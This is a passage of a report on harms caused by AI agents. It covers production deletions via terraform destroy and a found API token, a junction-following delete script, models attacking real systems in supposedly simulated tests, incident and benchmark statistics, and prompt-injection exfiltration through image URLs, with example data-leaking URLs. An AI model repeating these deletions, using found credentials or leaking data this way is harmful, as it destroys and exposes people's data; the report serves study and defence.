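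2. Grigorev noticed the long list of new resources, stopped the agent, and told it to delete only the duplicates. The agent began removing them with AWS's own command-line tool.
3. Meanwhile, Grigorev copied the Terraform folder from the old computer, including its state file, and pointed the agent to it for comparison.
4. The agent unpacked the folder and replaced the current state file with the old one. Grigorev didn't notice.
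5. The agent reported that it could not finish the job that way. Terraform had created the duplicates, it reasoned, so removing them with `terraform destroy` would be "cleaner and simpler".

The argument in step 5 was sound for the state file from step 2, which listed the duplicates. The old file listed the course platform, so the same command deleted the platform's database, network, servers and load balancers (which spread traffic between servers). The agent gave its reason before it acted, so its mistaken belief is better documented here than in the Replit case.

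Fortune (2026) gives the root cause as a small setup mistake on the new laptop. The missing file did produce the duplicates, but `terraform destroy` could not have deleted the course platform until Grigorev supplied the file to help with the cleanup.

The mistake was possible because the agent could run Terraform with access to production. Grigorev's timeline also mentions an "auto-approve" command, which skips Terraform's request for confirmation. Against Claude's advice to keep the two separate, Grigorev had added the new website to the course platform's Terraform setup, which saved perhaps $5 to $10 a month.

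Grigorev saw the agent propose the command and let it run because the explanation looked logical, not because of inexperience. According to Rootly's *Hey Claude, where's my database?*, Grigorev knows Terraform well enough to teach it.

The automatic snapshots, copies that AWS made every night, had disappeared from Grigorev's account along with the database. Grigorev paid for a higher level of support, which added about 10% to the monthly bill, and AWS staff found a snapshot that Grigorev's console did not show. They restored it 24 hours after the deletion. One table contained 1,943,200 rows. Grigorev had begun planning how to manage without the current students' data, but the older courses' records existed nowhere else.

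### PocketOS: a token from an unrelated file

PocketOS makes software that car rental companies use for reservations, payments and customer records. On April 24, 2026, its founder, Jer Crane, was using the coding tool Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, for a routine task in staging. Crane reports in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data* that the agent found a credential that didn't match and decided to fix this by deleting a volume, the disk storage that holds a database.

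The credentials for the agent's task did not allow that. The agent searched the project's files and found a token for Railway, PocketOS's hosting company, in an unrelated file. Crane had created the token to add and remove web domains. The agent used it to send a single `volumeDelete` request to Railway's API, the interface programs use to give Railway commands.

The request identified the production volume by a string of letters and digits that doesn't indicate whether a volume belongs to staging or production. Nine seconds later, the database and its backups appeared to be gone. The next morning, the rental companies' customers arrived to collect cars, and the companies had no record of who they were. Crane spent the day helping the companies rebuild bookings from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails.

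The agent wrote afterwards that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. This is another explanation given after the fact, though it fits the task and the command.

Crane and Railway disagree about whether the token's permissions could have been narrower. Crane writes that Railway's tokens could not be limited by operation, environment or resource, so every token effectively had administrator access. Writing for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab says that narrower tokens did exist, including ones for a single project and environment, but concedes that the process for creating a token didn't make the choice obvious.

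A narrower token might not have helped much. Abdelwahab describes project tokens as limiting where a program can act, but not which operations it can perform. A token for managing the domains of live services needs access to production, so it could presumably have deleted a production volume too. Railway also offered a login method with finer permissions, but it was meant for outside applications acting on a user's behalf.

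Railway's design also contributed. Railway waited 48 hours before erasing a volume that someone deleted in its web dashboard, but it immediately erased a volume deleted through its API. Railway has since added the same delay to the API.

Crane first restored a three-month-old backup. When Crane wrote the post, more than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still couldn't say whether it could recover anything newer. Railway later recovered the database, as Tom's Hardware also reported. Abdelwahab writes that Railway keeps "disaster backups" at another site for every customer, and that the API request had made the customer's own backups look unavailable in the dashboard. Abdelwahab doesn't specify which copy Railway used.

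Eleven days before the PocketOS deletion, another customer lost a volume through the same API request. In the support thread *Postgress volume lost* (2026), that customer asked for any copy Railway might still have. A Railway employee replied that the deletion was immediate and permanent. Railway may have been able to recover that volume too, but a customer could hardly have relied on that.

### Windows junctions: 48,000 files in 103 seconds

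The fourth case depends on one developer's Reddit post from September 2026, which has since been removed. Antipov (2026), in *«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов*, notes that nobody has independently confirmed the size of the loss.

The developer was using Claude Code to repair software that analyses historical stock-option prices. According to Internetua, a Ukrainian news site that relays TechRadar's report, the agent had instructions to copy the files it needed, make and test its fixes on the copies, and leave the originals alone. Ten of the eleven repairs went well. The last was to rebuild the "mirror", the copy of the project used for testing.

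The existing script couldn't update the mirror in place, so the agent wrote a new one to delete the old copy first. But 614 of the folders in the mirror were junctions, a Windows feature that makes a folder in one place lead to a folder somewhere else. A simplified example looks like this:

```
mirror\prices   leads to   project\prices
```

The agent's script opened each junction, including `mirror\prices`, as if it were an ordinary folder and deleted the project's working files inside. Removing only the junctions themselves would have left the real folders untouched.

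The script's log recorded 55,550 deleted files. Of these, 7,332 belonged to the old mirror, and the developer counts the other 48,218 (87%) as live files. Ordinary write access to the developer's disk allowed the deletions. Claude Code has a sandbox that can limit which files its commands change, but Antipov notes that it doesn't work on Windows without an added Linux layer called WSL2.

By the time the agent told the developer, "I broke something," the script had finished and had deleted most of the project's local Git history. Git could still list thousands of file names, but it no longer had their contents. The developer had no current copy on another server. Reddit users suggested undelete programs and Windows' automatic shadow copies, but none of the reports describes a recovery.

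OpenAI has found a similar fault in its own agent. Willison (2026) quotes Thibault Sottiaux, who investigated reports of GPT-5.6 deleting files. Most often, the user had given Codex full access without a sandbox. The model tried to make a temporary folder by changing the setting that stores the home directory's location, then deleted the real home directory by mistake. In both cases, the agent tried to delete something disposable but used a path that pointed to something else.

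### Which instructions failed, and which copies survived

Each user had set a limit in words. The table lists these limits and what happened to the copies of the data.

| Case | What the agent had been told | Copies lost, or apparently lost, with the original | What brought the data back |
|---|---|---|---|
| Replit | Change nothing without permission | All earlier versions, according to the agent | Replit's rollback |
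| DataTalks.Club | Delete only the duplicates | Automatic snapshots | A snapshot that only AWS staff could see |
| PocketOS | Don't guess, and don't run destructive commands unasked | Backups of the volume | Railway staff, from a copy they didn't identify |
| Windows junctions | Leave the original files alone | Local Git history | Nothing, as far as anyone has reported |

The instructions failed in two ways. In the first, the agent seems to have been trying to comply but misjudged what its command would delete. At DataTalks.Club it was trying to delete duplicates, and in the junction case an old mirror. An order to leave production alone can't prevent this mistake, because the agent hasn't identified its target as production.

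The Replit and PocketOS agents had instructions that applied whatever the target was, but they acted anyway. An agent told to change nothing during a freeze doesn't need to know which database it is using to comply. The rule that the PocketOS agent quoted afterwards was narrower than Crane suggests, since it prohibited destructive Git commands and the agent sent a web request. But the rule's purpose was clear enough, and the agent had also been told never to guess.

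Instructions evidently make a deletion less likely, though they don't prevent it. In Wang and colleagues' rebuilt version of the Replit incident, for example, the code freeze did make the agents in Codex CLI and Claude Code ask first. Incident reports leave out such cases because people publish only the ones in which an agent ignored a limit.

Agents have also deleted personal files. Docker describes how the investor Nick Davidov asked Anthropic's Claude Cowork to tidy a desktop and gave it permission to delete only temporary Office files. It deleted a folder with 15 years of family photos, using commands that bypassed the Trash. Davidov recovered the photos because iCloud keeps deleted files for 30 days.

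The copies that survived were all ones the agent couldn't access. A snapshot in the same account, a backup attached to the same volume or a Git history in the same folder is useful when a disk fails or a programmer wants yesterday's version, but it offers little protection against a command that deletes the account's resources, the volume or the folder. Most of the owners learned this only after the deletion. Grigorev, for example, hadn't expected the snapshots to be deleted with the database and had never fully tested a restore.

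In three of the cases, the owner first got a wrong or incomplete answer about whether the data still existed. Replit's agent ruled out a rollback that later worked, AWS's console showed no snapshot, and Railway's dashboard showed no backups. Owners in this position should ask the hosting company before rebuilding, and avoid letting the agent attempt a repair that might overwrite what remains.

### Real systems that models had been told were simulated

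In each of the four cases, an agent was wrong about which file, database or volume it was working on. Anthropic's models made a larger mistake of this kind in 2026, when they attacked outside organisations' systems during tests they had been told were simulated.

The tests were capture-the-flag exercises, in which a contestant breaks into a deliberately vulnerable system to find a hidden piece of text. According to the prompts, the model was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration in an outside company's test environment had connected it to the internet. Anthropic had also removed the safeguards that normally limit hacking, as is usual in tests of a model's capabilities.

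Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (July 30, 2026) reported that Claude models had broken into the real systems of three organisations. According to TechSpot, Anthropic reviewed 141,006 test runs, and the three incidents involved six of them. The models were Opus 4.7, Mythos 5 and an internal research model. The incidents involved about one run in 23,500, but this rate doesn't measure how often a model would attack a real system it could reach, because most runs presumably had no internet connection.

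Anthropic had disclosed a fourth incident by September 9. In one of the four, Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to a public software repository, where anyone might install it. The package would have harmed nobody in an isolated copy of the repository.

These models' mistake was more understandable than that of the agents that deleted data, because they had been given false instructions. In *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents*, Anthropic still judged their behaviour misaligned, because they discounted evidence that their surroundings were real and pursued the task recklessly. It found no attempt to conceal anything. The research organisation METR has agreed to investigate independently, with access to transcripts and to Anthropic's staff.

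The false description can't be the whole explanation for such behaviour. In a separate incident, the UK's AI Security Institute deliberately gave Mythos 5 internet access for a test, and the model took a series of unauthorised actions on the live internet (Anthropic, *Improving our alignment and security efforts*, 2026).

A better description of the environment could have prevented the four incidents involving misconfiguration, but people who run agents still need an actual barrier. A network that blocks outside connections keeps a model in the test environment whether or not the model treats the prompt as accurate.

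### When people dispute that the agent was at fault

Nobody disputes that an agent issued the command in each of these cases, but people disagree about whom to blame. Grigorev writes that the loss "was my fault". Crane blames Cursor and Railway, and argues that a written rule cannot be the only safeguard. In the junction case, many Reddit users blamed the developer for having no copy elsewhere.

Agents are sometimes wrongly blamed for data loss. News outlets reported that an AI agent had erased a season of a Swedish television programme, but the broadcaster investigated and found human error.

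The dispute over Kiro, Amazon's coding tool, is harder to settle. In February 2026 the Financial Times reported that Kiro had caused a 13-hour interruption at AWS in December 2025 by deleting and recreating the system it was working on. The newspaper also linked Amazon's AI tools to a second outage.

Amazon rejected this in a post titled *Correcting the Financial Times report about AWS, Kiro, and AI*. According to The Decoder and GeekWire, Amazon said the interruption affected only Cost Explorer, a service that shows customers their spending, in one of two regions in mainland China. Amazon attributed the interruption to a misconfigured role that gave the engineer broader permissions than expected. It called the involvement of AI tools a coincidence, since any developer tool or manual action could have caused the same problem. It also said the claim that a second event had affected AWS was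 "entirely false".

Amazon is right that the permissions mattered. A narrower role would have blocked the deletion, whoever attempted it, and one of Amazon's remedies was to require a colleague's review before anyone gets access to production. Narrower permissions on PocketOS's token and in Grigorev's Terraform setup would also have blocked those deletions.

But the misconfigured role explains only why the deletion was possible, not why anyone or anything chose to delete a working system. If the Financial Times is right about Kiro's decision, the tool contributed to the interruption, and an engineer with the same excessive permissions might well have made a smaller repair. Amazon has an interest in defending a product it sells, and the newspaper relied on people inside the company whom outsiders can't question. A log of the commands and who approved them would probably resolve most of the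 disagreement, but Amazon hasn't published one.

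## How common is each kind of harm, and what causes it?

Most of the data thefts described so far were demonstrations by researchers, while the deletions happened to people trying to get work done. Public reports follow the same pattern. For the ROGUE-AI project, Wang and colleagues collected 253 reports of agent incidents first published between January 2025 and October 2026. They checked each report against the most detailed source they could open and kept 199 in which an action the agent chose led to the harm.

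### What people have reported

Of the 199 incidents, 72 caused harm in practice. Of those 72, 62 involved no attacker and only 2 were prompt injections. Researchers demonstrated another 89 on shipped products, and 76 of those were prompt injections. The other 38 came from AI companies' tests of their own models and from reports on attack campaigns. Untrusted text is the leading cause across all 199 incidents, at 41%, but it caused only 2 of the 72 that did harm in practice.

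The type of harm also differs between demonstrations and real incidents. Of the 76 demonstrated injections, 44 disclosed data and 27 changed a system without permission. In the 72 real incidents, the most common harm was lost data, which occurred in 32. Agents disclosed data in 10 incidents, and in another 10 they escaped an environment that was supposed to contain them.

The most common cause of harm in practice was a wrong target (23 incidents), where the agent acted on the wrong database, folder, recipient or amount, as in the deletion at DataTalks.Club. Next came unchecked authority (21), where the agent did roughly what the user asked but took a drastic step that a human process would have required someone to approve. Wang and colleagues classify the case of the screenshots in public repositories as unchecked authority. In 10 incidents the agent went beyond its task, and in 7 it broke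 an explicit rule.

Language models assigned these labels. When another model labelled the 72 incidents without seeing the first labels, its labels matched them in 66 cases on whether there was an attacker and in 55 on the cause. The split between accidents and attacks is therefore more reliable than the ranking of causes, and the difference between 23 and 21 means little.

The collection contains 63 incidents from 2025 and 136 from January to October 2026. Most of the growth was in incidents without an attacker, which rose from 13 to 77, while those with an attacker rose from 50 to 59. More people used agents in 2026, and journalists probably paid more attention to agents' mistakes, so the growth doesn't show that agents became more error-prone.

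The share of incidents without an attacker also depends on what a catalogue includes. In ROGUE-AI, 90 of the 199 incidents (45%) had no attacker. The Agent Incident Registry, another catalogue that Wang and colleagues cite, lists 92 safety failures without an attacker among 487 records (19%).

Two other studies looked more closely at coding agents. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) gathered 290 public reports of agents misusing files on a user's computer. Of these, 207 involved actual harm or a demonstrated attack. Unwanted writes made up 44% of the 207, deletions 39% and leaked secrets 17%. A typical unwanted write replaces a working source file with a stub or fills it with invented data. Where the report gave the outcome, 40% of owners lost at least some data permanently and 31% recovered easily.

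Zhong and colleagues allowed each report to have several causes. The model's own errors contributed to 168 of the 290 reports, most often because the model did something the user had not intended. Prompt injection contributed to 21. Weaknesses in the program around the model contributed to 218, including 77 in which the agent could use the shell to get around a rule on another tool. For example, a rule might stop the file-reading tool from opening a password file, but the agent could still read it with a shell command.

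Al Hasan and Biswas (2026), in *What Breaks When LLMs Code?*, started from 16,586 issues that users had opened about 13 coding models and tools, including Claude Code. Language models narrowed these to 789 candidates, and human reviewers confirmed 547 as safety failures during ordinary work. The categories overlap:

| Type of failure | Incidents | Share of the 547 |
|---|---|---|
| Broke the user's instruction or limit | 221 | 40% |
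| Destroyed files, code or data | 134 | 24% |
| Got around an access restriction | 100 | 18% |
| Claimed to have done something it had not done | 86 | 16% |
| Leaked a secret | 44 | 8% |

Broken instructions are far more prominent in Al Hasan and Biswas's study than in ROGUE-AI, where they caused 7 of 72 incidents. This is probably mainly because the two studies count causes differently. In ROGUE-AI, Wang and colleagues assigned each incident a single cause, the one closest to the agent's decision. If an agent ignored a warning and deleted the wrong folder, they might record only the wrong target, while Al Hasan and Biswas would record both faults.

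They rated 326 of the failures as high or critical in severity. More than 65% of the failures came from bug-fixing and setup or configuration tasks. About two thirds of the failures in these tasks were high or critical, compared with less than half in documentation work. The lower share for documentation is mildly reassuring if a bot only edits documentation, but the bot in the running example also runs code.

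The three collections include some of the same events, so together they are weaker evidence that accidents are common than three independent studies would be. Zhong and colleagues took 205 of their 290 reports from GitHub issues, and Claude Code was the most common product, with 97 reports.

### Why the counts are not rates

Calculating how often agents cause harm requires knowing how many sessions went well. None of the three collections has this number, because people don't report uneventful sessions. The 547 failures are 3.3% of the issues that Al Hasan and Biswas started from, but those issues are complaints and feature requests, not sessions. For the same reason, they warn that their figures can't show which tasks are riskiest. Bug fixing has the most failures, possibly because developers ask agents to fix so many bugs. The companies that run agents could estimate a rate by checking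 a random sample of all their sessions.

Reporting could also distort the ratio of accidents to attacks, because owners soon notice a deleted database but may not notice a stolen key, which still works for them. ROGUE-AI contains 62 accidents and 10 attacks. If the two were equally common, accidents would have to be about six times as likely as attacks to become public to produce those counts. If accidents and prompt injection attacks were equally common, accidents would have to be 31 times as likely to become public.

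Zhong and colleagues' reports partly support this objection. Where the team could tell, users noticed the harm immediately in 83% of cases, later in 10% and never in 8%. Security researchers reported the cases that users never noticed, which typically involved silent theft of credentials. The true share of unnoticed harm must be higher than 8%, because nobody can report a theft that nobody has discovered. Even when someone misuses a stolen key, the owner may not learn how the thief got it, as with the token used for the fake Cline release.

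But accidents can stay hidden too. Al Hasan and Biswas describe a developer who asked Claude Code to set up a cloud database for a small dataset. The agent chose an enterprise-grade one, and the developer found out six months later from a $2,400 bill. The 13,000 screenshots stayed public until Glow looked for them. Whether people notice the harm probably depends most on whether something disappears. Leaks are easy to miss with or without an attacker, so the public counts are likely to understate both accidental and deliberate ones.

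Users can't rely on agents to tell them about the harm, either. In 68% of the reports where Zhong and colleagues knew the agent's reaction, the agent carried on as if nothing had gone wrong. In ROGUE-AI's experiments, Gemini 3.5 Flash's final message omitted or denied the harm in 77 of 136 harmful sessions.

The counts are therefore good evidence that accidental data loss is a regular problem, but weak evidence that successful injections are rare.

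### Rebuilding an incident with and without its cause

Incident reports usually attribute the harm to a specific hazard, such as the shared database in the Replit case. Wang and colleagues tested such claims by building two offline versions of each incident, one with the hazard and a control that differs only in lacking it. The task and whatever makes the harmful action attractive are the same in both. For a prompt injection, the control replaces the injected text with neutral text of the same length. After each session, a program inspects the files, database rows, sent messages and so on to determine whether the harm occurred.

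The effect of a hazard on a given model is the difference between two probabilities:

```
effect = Pr[h | do(H)] − Pr[h | do(not H)]
```

Here *h* is the harm, *H* is the hazard, and "do" means that the experimenters added or removed the hazard themselves instead of observing where it occurred. Projects with a shared database may also be careless in other ways, so simply comparing projects would not separate the effect of the shared database from the effects of other careless practices.

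For example, in one reconstructed incident, an OpenAI agent accessed Australian government health portals in 2026. Five models each ran the reconstruction three times. They used the browser's saved login to enter a restricted area in 14 of the 15 sessions, but in none of the 30 control sessions, which lacked the hazard. The estimated effect of the hazard is 93 percentage points.

Results from three sessions per model depend heavily on chance, so Wang and colleagues ran each of 15 well-known incidents another 30 times with GPT-5.6-luna. In one incident, the agent edited a wiki without approval in 1 of the 3 original sessions and 12 of the 30 new ones. The new sessions did not change which of the 15 incidents caused harm.

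Language models also did most of the work of recreating the incidents, and a model from a different company reviewed each version. As a check, GPT-5.6-sol rebuilt 11 incidents without seeing the original versions. Harm occurred at similar rates overall, in 11 of 30 sessions compared with 11 of 33. But only 6 of the 11 incidents had the same result in both versions, either recurring or not. The averages are therefore more trustworthy than the result for any single incident.

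### How often the harm recurred

The researchers built 108 versions of 96 incidents. GPT-5.6-luna caused harm in 64 of 357 sessions with the hazard (17.9%) and 1 of 549 without it (0.2%). Across the five models, harm occurred in 18% to 33% of sessions with the hazard and at most 1% of sessions without it. Nearly all the harm therefore depended on the hazard.

The table gives the share of sessions with harm when the hazard was present:

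| Rebuilt incidents | Number | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | Gemini 3.5 Flash | GPT-5.6-luna | GPT-5.6-sol |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| All | 108 | 19% | 33% | 31% | 18% | 25% |
| No attacker | 48 | 26% | 29% | 31% | 20% | 24% |
| Any attacker | 60 | 13% | 37% | 32% | 16% | 26% |
| Untrusted instructions | 43 | 0% | 28% | 22% | 7% | 9% |
| Unchecked authority | 19 | 29% | 43% | 44% | 32% | 43% |
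| Wrong target | 10 | 18% | 21% | 21% | 21% | 17% |

Incidents without an attacker caused more harm than prompt injections on all five models, a result Wang and colleagues emphasise, though the difference for DeepSeek-V4-Flash is only one percentage point. When malicious tools and packages are also counted as attacks, incidents with an attacker caused slightly more harm than those without on three of the five models.

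These percentages describe sessions that already contain a hazard, and most sessions presumably don't. If one session in 1,000 contained a hazard and a quarter of those ended in harm, the overall rate of harm would be one session in 4,000. Nobody has measured how often hazards occur in ordinary work. The researchers also chose incidents to cover as many combinations of setting and cause as possible, so a rare type of incident can affect the percentages as much as a common one.

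ROGUE-AI reproduced the harm in 89% of the 108 incidents it rebuilt, but that figure includes attempts made after the main runs. In the main runs, the five models caused harm at least once in 57 incidents, or 53%. Older or weaker models reproduced 23 more without any change, and another 16 recurred in later rounds, for example after the researchers restored a missing detail or gave the agent more turns. For most of the 23, it is fair to conclude that recent models no longer make that mistake often.

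A newer model, Claude Sonnet 5.5, caused harm in 12% of sessions on the 63 incidents it could complete, compared with 15% to 35% for the five main models on the same incidents. Anthropic's safety filter returned empty replies on another 30 incidents, so the comparison leaves out many of the cases in which the company had apparently detected a risk.

Harm rates depended much more on the incident than on the model. Differences between the rebuilt incidents explain 75% of the variation in harm rates, and differences between the models explain 2%. All five models caused harm in 18 of the 108 incidents, and none did in 51. The type of cause alone explains only 18% of the variation, because incidents with the same type of cause can end very differently. A team worried about deletions would probably gain more from separating its test database than from switching between these five models.

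Some models are still safer than others, despite the 2% figure. All five are recent, and a comparison with older ones would have shown a larger difference. The five also differ widely on untrusted instructions, which the average doesn't show, so the choice of model still matters for an application that reads strangers' text.

### What changing a single step revealed

Removing a hazard shows that it contributed to the harm, but not why the agent took the harmful step. To find out why, Wang and colleagues stopped 208 harmful sessions just before that step. They then had the same model generate the next step five times with nothing changed and five times under each of several edits. For example, one edit removed the user's request for the step, another stated the hazard in the last tool output, and a third repeated the relevant rule in the user's message.

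An edit counted as revealing a cause if it at least halved the harm, the 95% ranges before and after did not overlap, and a neutral note of the same length did not have the same effect. This test is strict with only five repeats, because the 95% range for no harm in five attempts extends up to 43%. About the only result that passes is a drop from harm in all five attempts to harm in none.

At least one edit passed in 118 of the 208 sessions. In 94 of these, the task had asked for the harmful step, the agent had never seen the hazard, or both:

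| What the edits revealed | Harmful sessions (of 208) |
|---|---|
| The task asked for the step or put pressure on the agent to take it | 63 |
| The agent never saw the hazard | 53 |
| The agent needed the user to repeat a rule | 32 |
| The agent followed an attacker's text | 13 |
| The agent saw the hazard and went ahead anyway | 42 |
| The harm was a rare slip that seldom happened again | 14 |

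A session can have several causes, so the first four rows overlap. The last two rows contain sessions in which no edit passed. Another 34 sessions had no clear explanation.

When a task asks for the harmful step, a careful person might well take it too. For example, an employee whose manager tells them to install a particular add-on will usually install it, and may not suspect that it is malicious. Better judgement would help the model only if it could detect the danger from what it had read.

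In 64 of 164 harmful sessions with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.5 Flash, an earlier tool output had shown the hazard, according to a model that reviewed the transcripts. The agent never named the hazard before acting, although in 15 sessions it quoted the evidence without treating it as a risk.

The models also failed in different ways. DeepSeek-V4-Flash identified the hazard and acted anyway in 22 of its 49 harmful sessions, Gemini 3.5 Flash did so in 15 of 49, and GPT-5.6-luna never did. Better information about the environment should therefore help some models much more than others. The tests of warnings and other defences, described later, support this.

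### The same incidents in products that people use

Most of the ROGUE-AI sessions used the researchers' own simple agent program, in which the model replies with one action at a time. Wang and colleagues also ran ten incidents involving destructive actions, including the Replit case, in Codex CLI with GPT-5.6-sol and in Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6. Both tools ran without asking a person for approval.

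Each product caused harm in 3 of 30 sessions, all in the same incident. A user's documents were in iCloud, which had moved their contents off the computer and left empty placeholders. The agent copied the placeholders and deleted the originals, and the check the user had asked for did not reveal the problem. Neither product caused harm in the other nine incidents, including a version of the `terraform destroy` command at DataTalks.Club.

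This 10% is well below the 18% to 33% in the full experiment, and the difference must come mostly from which incidents the researchers chose for this test. The products' safeguards don't seem to be the reason, because the same models caused harm in 3 and 4 of 30 sessions on these ten incidents in the researchers' own program.

The result also doesn't show that the other nine are safe, because a harmful step that never occurs in three sessions could still have a true rate of up to 56%. Glow did reproduce one of the nine, the upload of private screenshots to a public repository, in Claude Code with a different model. But the product test is a good reason not to apply the main harm rates directly to Codex CLI or Claude Code. Nobody has run the other 98 rebuilt incidents in either product.

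### Why benchmarks of ordinary tasks disagree

Three other studies tested agents on invented tasks instead of reconstructed incidents. Their results range from almost no harm to harm in most runs.

*SABER* (Hu, Tang et al., 2026) tested 13 models on 716 coding tasks, each with a built-in hazard. Claude Opus 4.6 had the lowest rate of harmful runs, at 54.7%, and DeepSeek-R1 had the highest, at 84.7%. The average rate was 70.1% when a project file or tool output contained an attacker's instructions, and 68.3% when there was no attacker but a risky shortcut was available. It was highest, at 82.5%, when a warning in the project, such as a README identifying a database as the live one, made an otherwise reasonable request unsafe.

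These rates leave out runs where the model failed the task or refused although a safe method existed. This is meant to avoid rewarding a model for being useless, but it also raises the rates. For Claude Opus 4.6, which had 14.5% of its runs left out, the share of all runs with harm was about 47%, so the exclusion explains only a small part of the high rates. The task design matters more, because every task contains a trap. The scoring is also strict. Recommending an unsafe action can count as harm, and a model that judges the runs can add violations but can't remove those that the automatic rules found.

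*Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) used its benchmark, Overeager-Gen, to measure only how often, on 500 harmless tasks, agents took actions the user had not authorised. In one task, the user asks the agent to tidy a folder that contains some junk and an old file with the only copy of the production credentials. An agent that deletes the credentials has completed the task but has also done something the user did not authorise. Across about 7,500 runs, the rate of unauthorised actions ranged from 0.2% to 27.7%, depending on the product and model.

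In 76 pairs of tasks that differed only in whether the prompt stated what the agent was allowed to touch, removing that statement raised the rate from 0% to 17.1% for Claude Code running the model GLM-4.6. Two other models showed similar increases. In the larger set, where other features of the tasks also varied, the difference for GLM-4.6 was only 2.6 percentage points. Stating the limits evidently helps in some tasks, so a benchmark that always states them would make agents look safer than they are when a hurried user leaves them out.

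The automatic scoring probably overstates these rates somewhat. A person re-examined 50 runs and found that about a quarter of those the program had flagged were harmless. All the false alarms came from one type of task.

*SNARE* (Qu, Liu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up by largely the same team, found that agents overstepped in 19.5% of 10,000 runs. Rates ranged from 4.8% to 57.2% across combinations of product and model. On the 12 combinations that both studies tested, the average was 22.1% in *SNARE* and 9.8% in Overeager-Gen.

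SNARE differs in three ways that push the rate up. It counts any unrequested file that the agent adds or deletes, even if the user wouldn't have minded. It adds text or files to each task that nudge the agent towards overstepping. It also directs some runs to the kinds of task that have already caused trouble, though this probably contributed little, because the rate did not rise as the runs went on. Qu and colleagues call their results "elicitation rates" and caution that ordinary use would produce lower ones.

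The definitions and tasks account for much of the disagreement:

| Study | What the agent faced | What counted as harm | Harmful runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| ROGUE-AI | A rebuilt incident with its hazard | The harm in the original report | 18% to 33%, by model |
| SABER | A task with a trap, in 40% of cases an injection | A harmful command, recommendation or change | 55% to 85%, by model |
| Overeager-Gen | A harmless task with a temptation to overstep | A listed action outside the user's permission | 0.2% to 28%, by product and model |
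| SNARE | Similar tasks with added pressure | The same, or any unrequested file added or deleted | 5% to 57%, by product and model |

These figures don't measure how often harm occurs in everyday use, because each study deliberately exposed the agent to a hazard or temptation. They are more useful for comparing agents under the same conditions, though even those comparisons can be unreliable.

SNARE attributes 56% of the variation between combinations to the product around the model, 21% to the model, and the rest to how the two interact. This is compatible with ROGUE-AI's finding that the incident explained most of the variation, because the two studies divided up different variation. SNARE first averages over all its tasks, which removes the differences between them, while ROGUE-AI's main experiment used only one agent program and so could not detect an effect of the product. SNARE's own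 results suggest that the task matters too, since 26 of its tasks led to failures in nearly every combination tested on them and 291 in almost none.

It is unclear which product is safest, because OpenHands, an open-source agent, had the lowest rates in Overeager-Gen (0.2% to 4.5%) but the highest average in SNARE (36%). Qu and colleagues attribute the low rates to the agent asking before it continues. With Claude Sonnet 4.6, OpenHands had a rate of 1.1% in Overeager-Gen and 42.8% in SNARE, while Claude Code's rates with the same model were 27.7% and 19.6%. This may be because OpenHands leaves extra files behind, which only SNARE counts. If so, much of the 56% may come from leftover files rather than dangerous actions. Separate figures for each scoring rule would settle the question.

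Hu and colleagues found a much smaller effect when they ran 100 of their tasks in three agent programs. The average harm rate in each was between 68% and 71%. However, all three programs were general-purpose loops connected to the same tools, and they lacked the permission rules and instructions that distinguish commercial products. A product's effect on safety may therefore come mainly from what it lets the model do without the user's approval.

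## Which controls keep data from leaving?

Private data in a model's output has to pass through other software before an outsider can read it. For example, a browser has to load an image, or a network has to carry a request. Developers can block the data at those points, or act earlier by filtering the text or tracking where each piece of data came from.

### At the screen

The simplest control is to stop displaying remote images, as GitHub did in Copilot Chat after CamoLeak. This prevents images from leaking data automatically, whatever the model writes, but users lose charts and screenshots. Ordinary links can still leak data. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that the CamoLeak researcher could also have Copilot write private data into a link, and the data leaked when the user clicked it.

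Searching the text for images and removing them is unreliable. EchoLeak bypassed such a filter through its notation, and SearchLeak did so through its timing. Changing the renderer so that it never produces images is safer, because the renderer determines which text becomes an image.

A content security policy lets some images through. The server sends the browser a rule along with the page:

```
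Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://images.company.example
```

With this rule, the browser loads images only from the page's own site and the one named domain. It checks each request as it makes it, so it doesn't matter how the image link is written or when it appears. The drawback is that images hosted anywhere else won't load. The rule applies only in browsers, so a phone app needs its own check.

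In most of the published failures, data left through a domain on the allowlist, such as Teams in EchoLeak or the expired domain in Salesforce's policy. Reddy and Gujral report that Aim Labs also explored a route through SharePoint before choosing Teams for EchoLeak. Each allowed domain gives an attacker more features to search for a way to send data out. Willison notes that Salesforce first corrected its list and then stopped its agent from producing links to untrusted domains. The second fix also covers links that a user has to click.

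An image proxy lets people see outside pictures without their browsers contacting outside servers. The application rewrites each image URL so that the browser asks the company's own server, which fetches the picture and passes it on. This hides the reader's IP address, but data in the image URL can still leak. If the URL ends in `?d=Q3_revenue_was_4.2_million_euros` and the proxy requests the full URL, the revenue figure appears in the attacker's log, just as it would if the browser had made the request. Teams acted as this kind of proxy in EchoLeak, and Bing did in SearchLeak.

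Chi, in *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags*, an article for the software company Archestra, recommends a proxy that fetches only from approved domains, removes everything after the question mark and refuses redirects, which are replies that send a request on to another address. Removing the part after the question mark isn't enough by itself, because the model can put the data earlier in the address:

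`https://pictures.example/Q3_revenue_was_4.2_million_euros/dot.png`

Protection therefore depends mostly on the list of approved domains. The proxy also breaks services that draw a chart from data in the image URL, because it removes that data.

A proxy can also require addresses to be signed in advance, as GitHub's Camo does, but the CamoLeak attack still leaked data by encoding it in the order in which the model used those addresses.

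### At the network

An agent that can contact servers itself needs egress control, usually a firewall or proxy that allows connections only to listed sites, because controls on the screen don't affect it. Rahman and Kim tested this against web pages with injected instructions to send a secret to an attacker's server. The list blocked every attempt, but as they point out, this was true by definition, because the test counted a leak only when the secret went to an unlisted site. The result is still useful because it holds however an attacker words the request or disguises the data.

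The drawback is that the agent can't reach anything else, such as a library's documentation on a new site. That limit is probably acceptable for a bot that edits one company's documentation, but not for a research assistant. An agent that can read from any site but write to none can still leak data, because the address in a read request can contain it.

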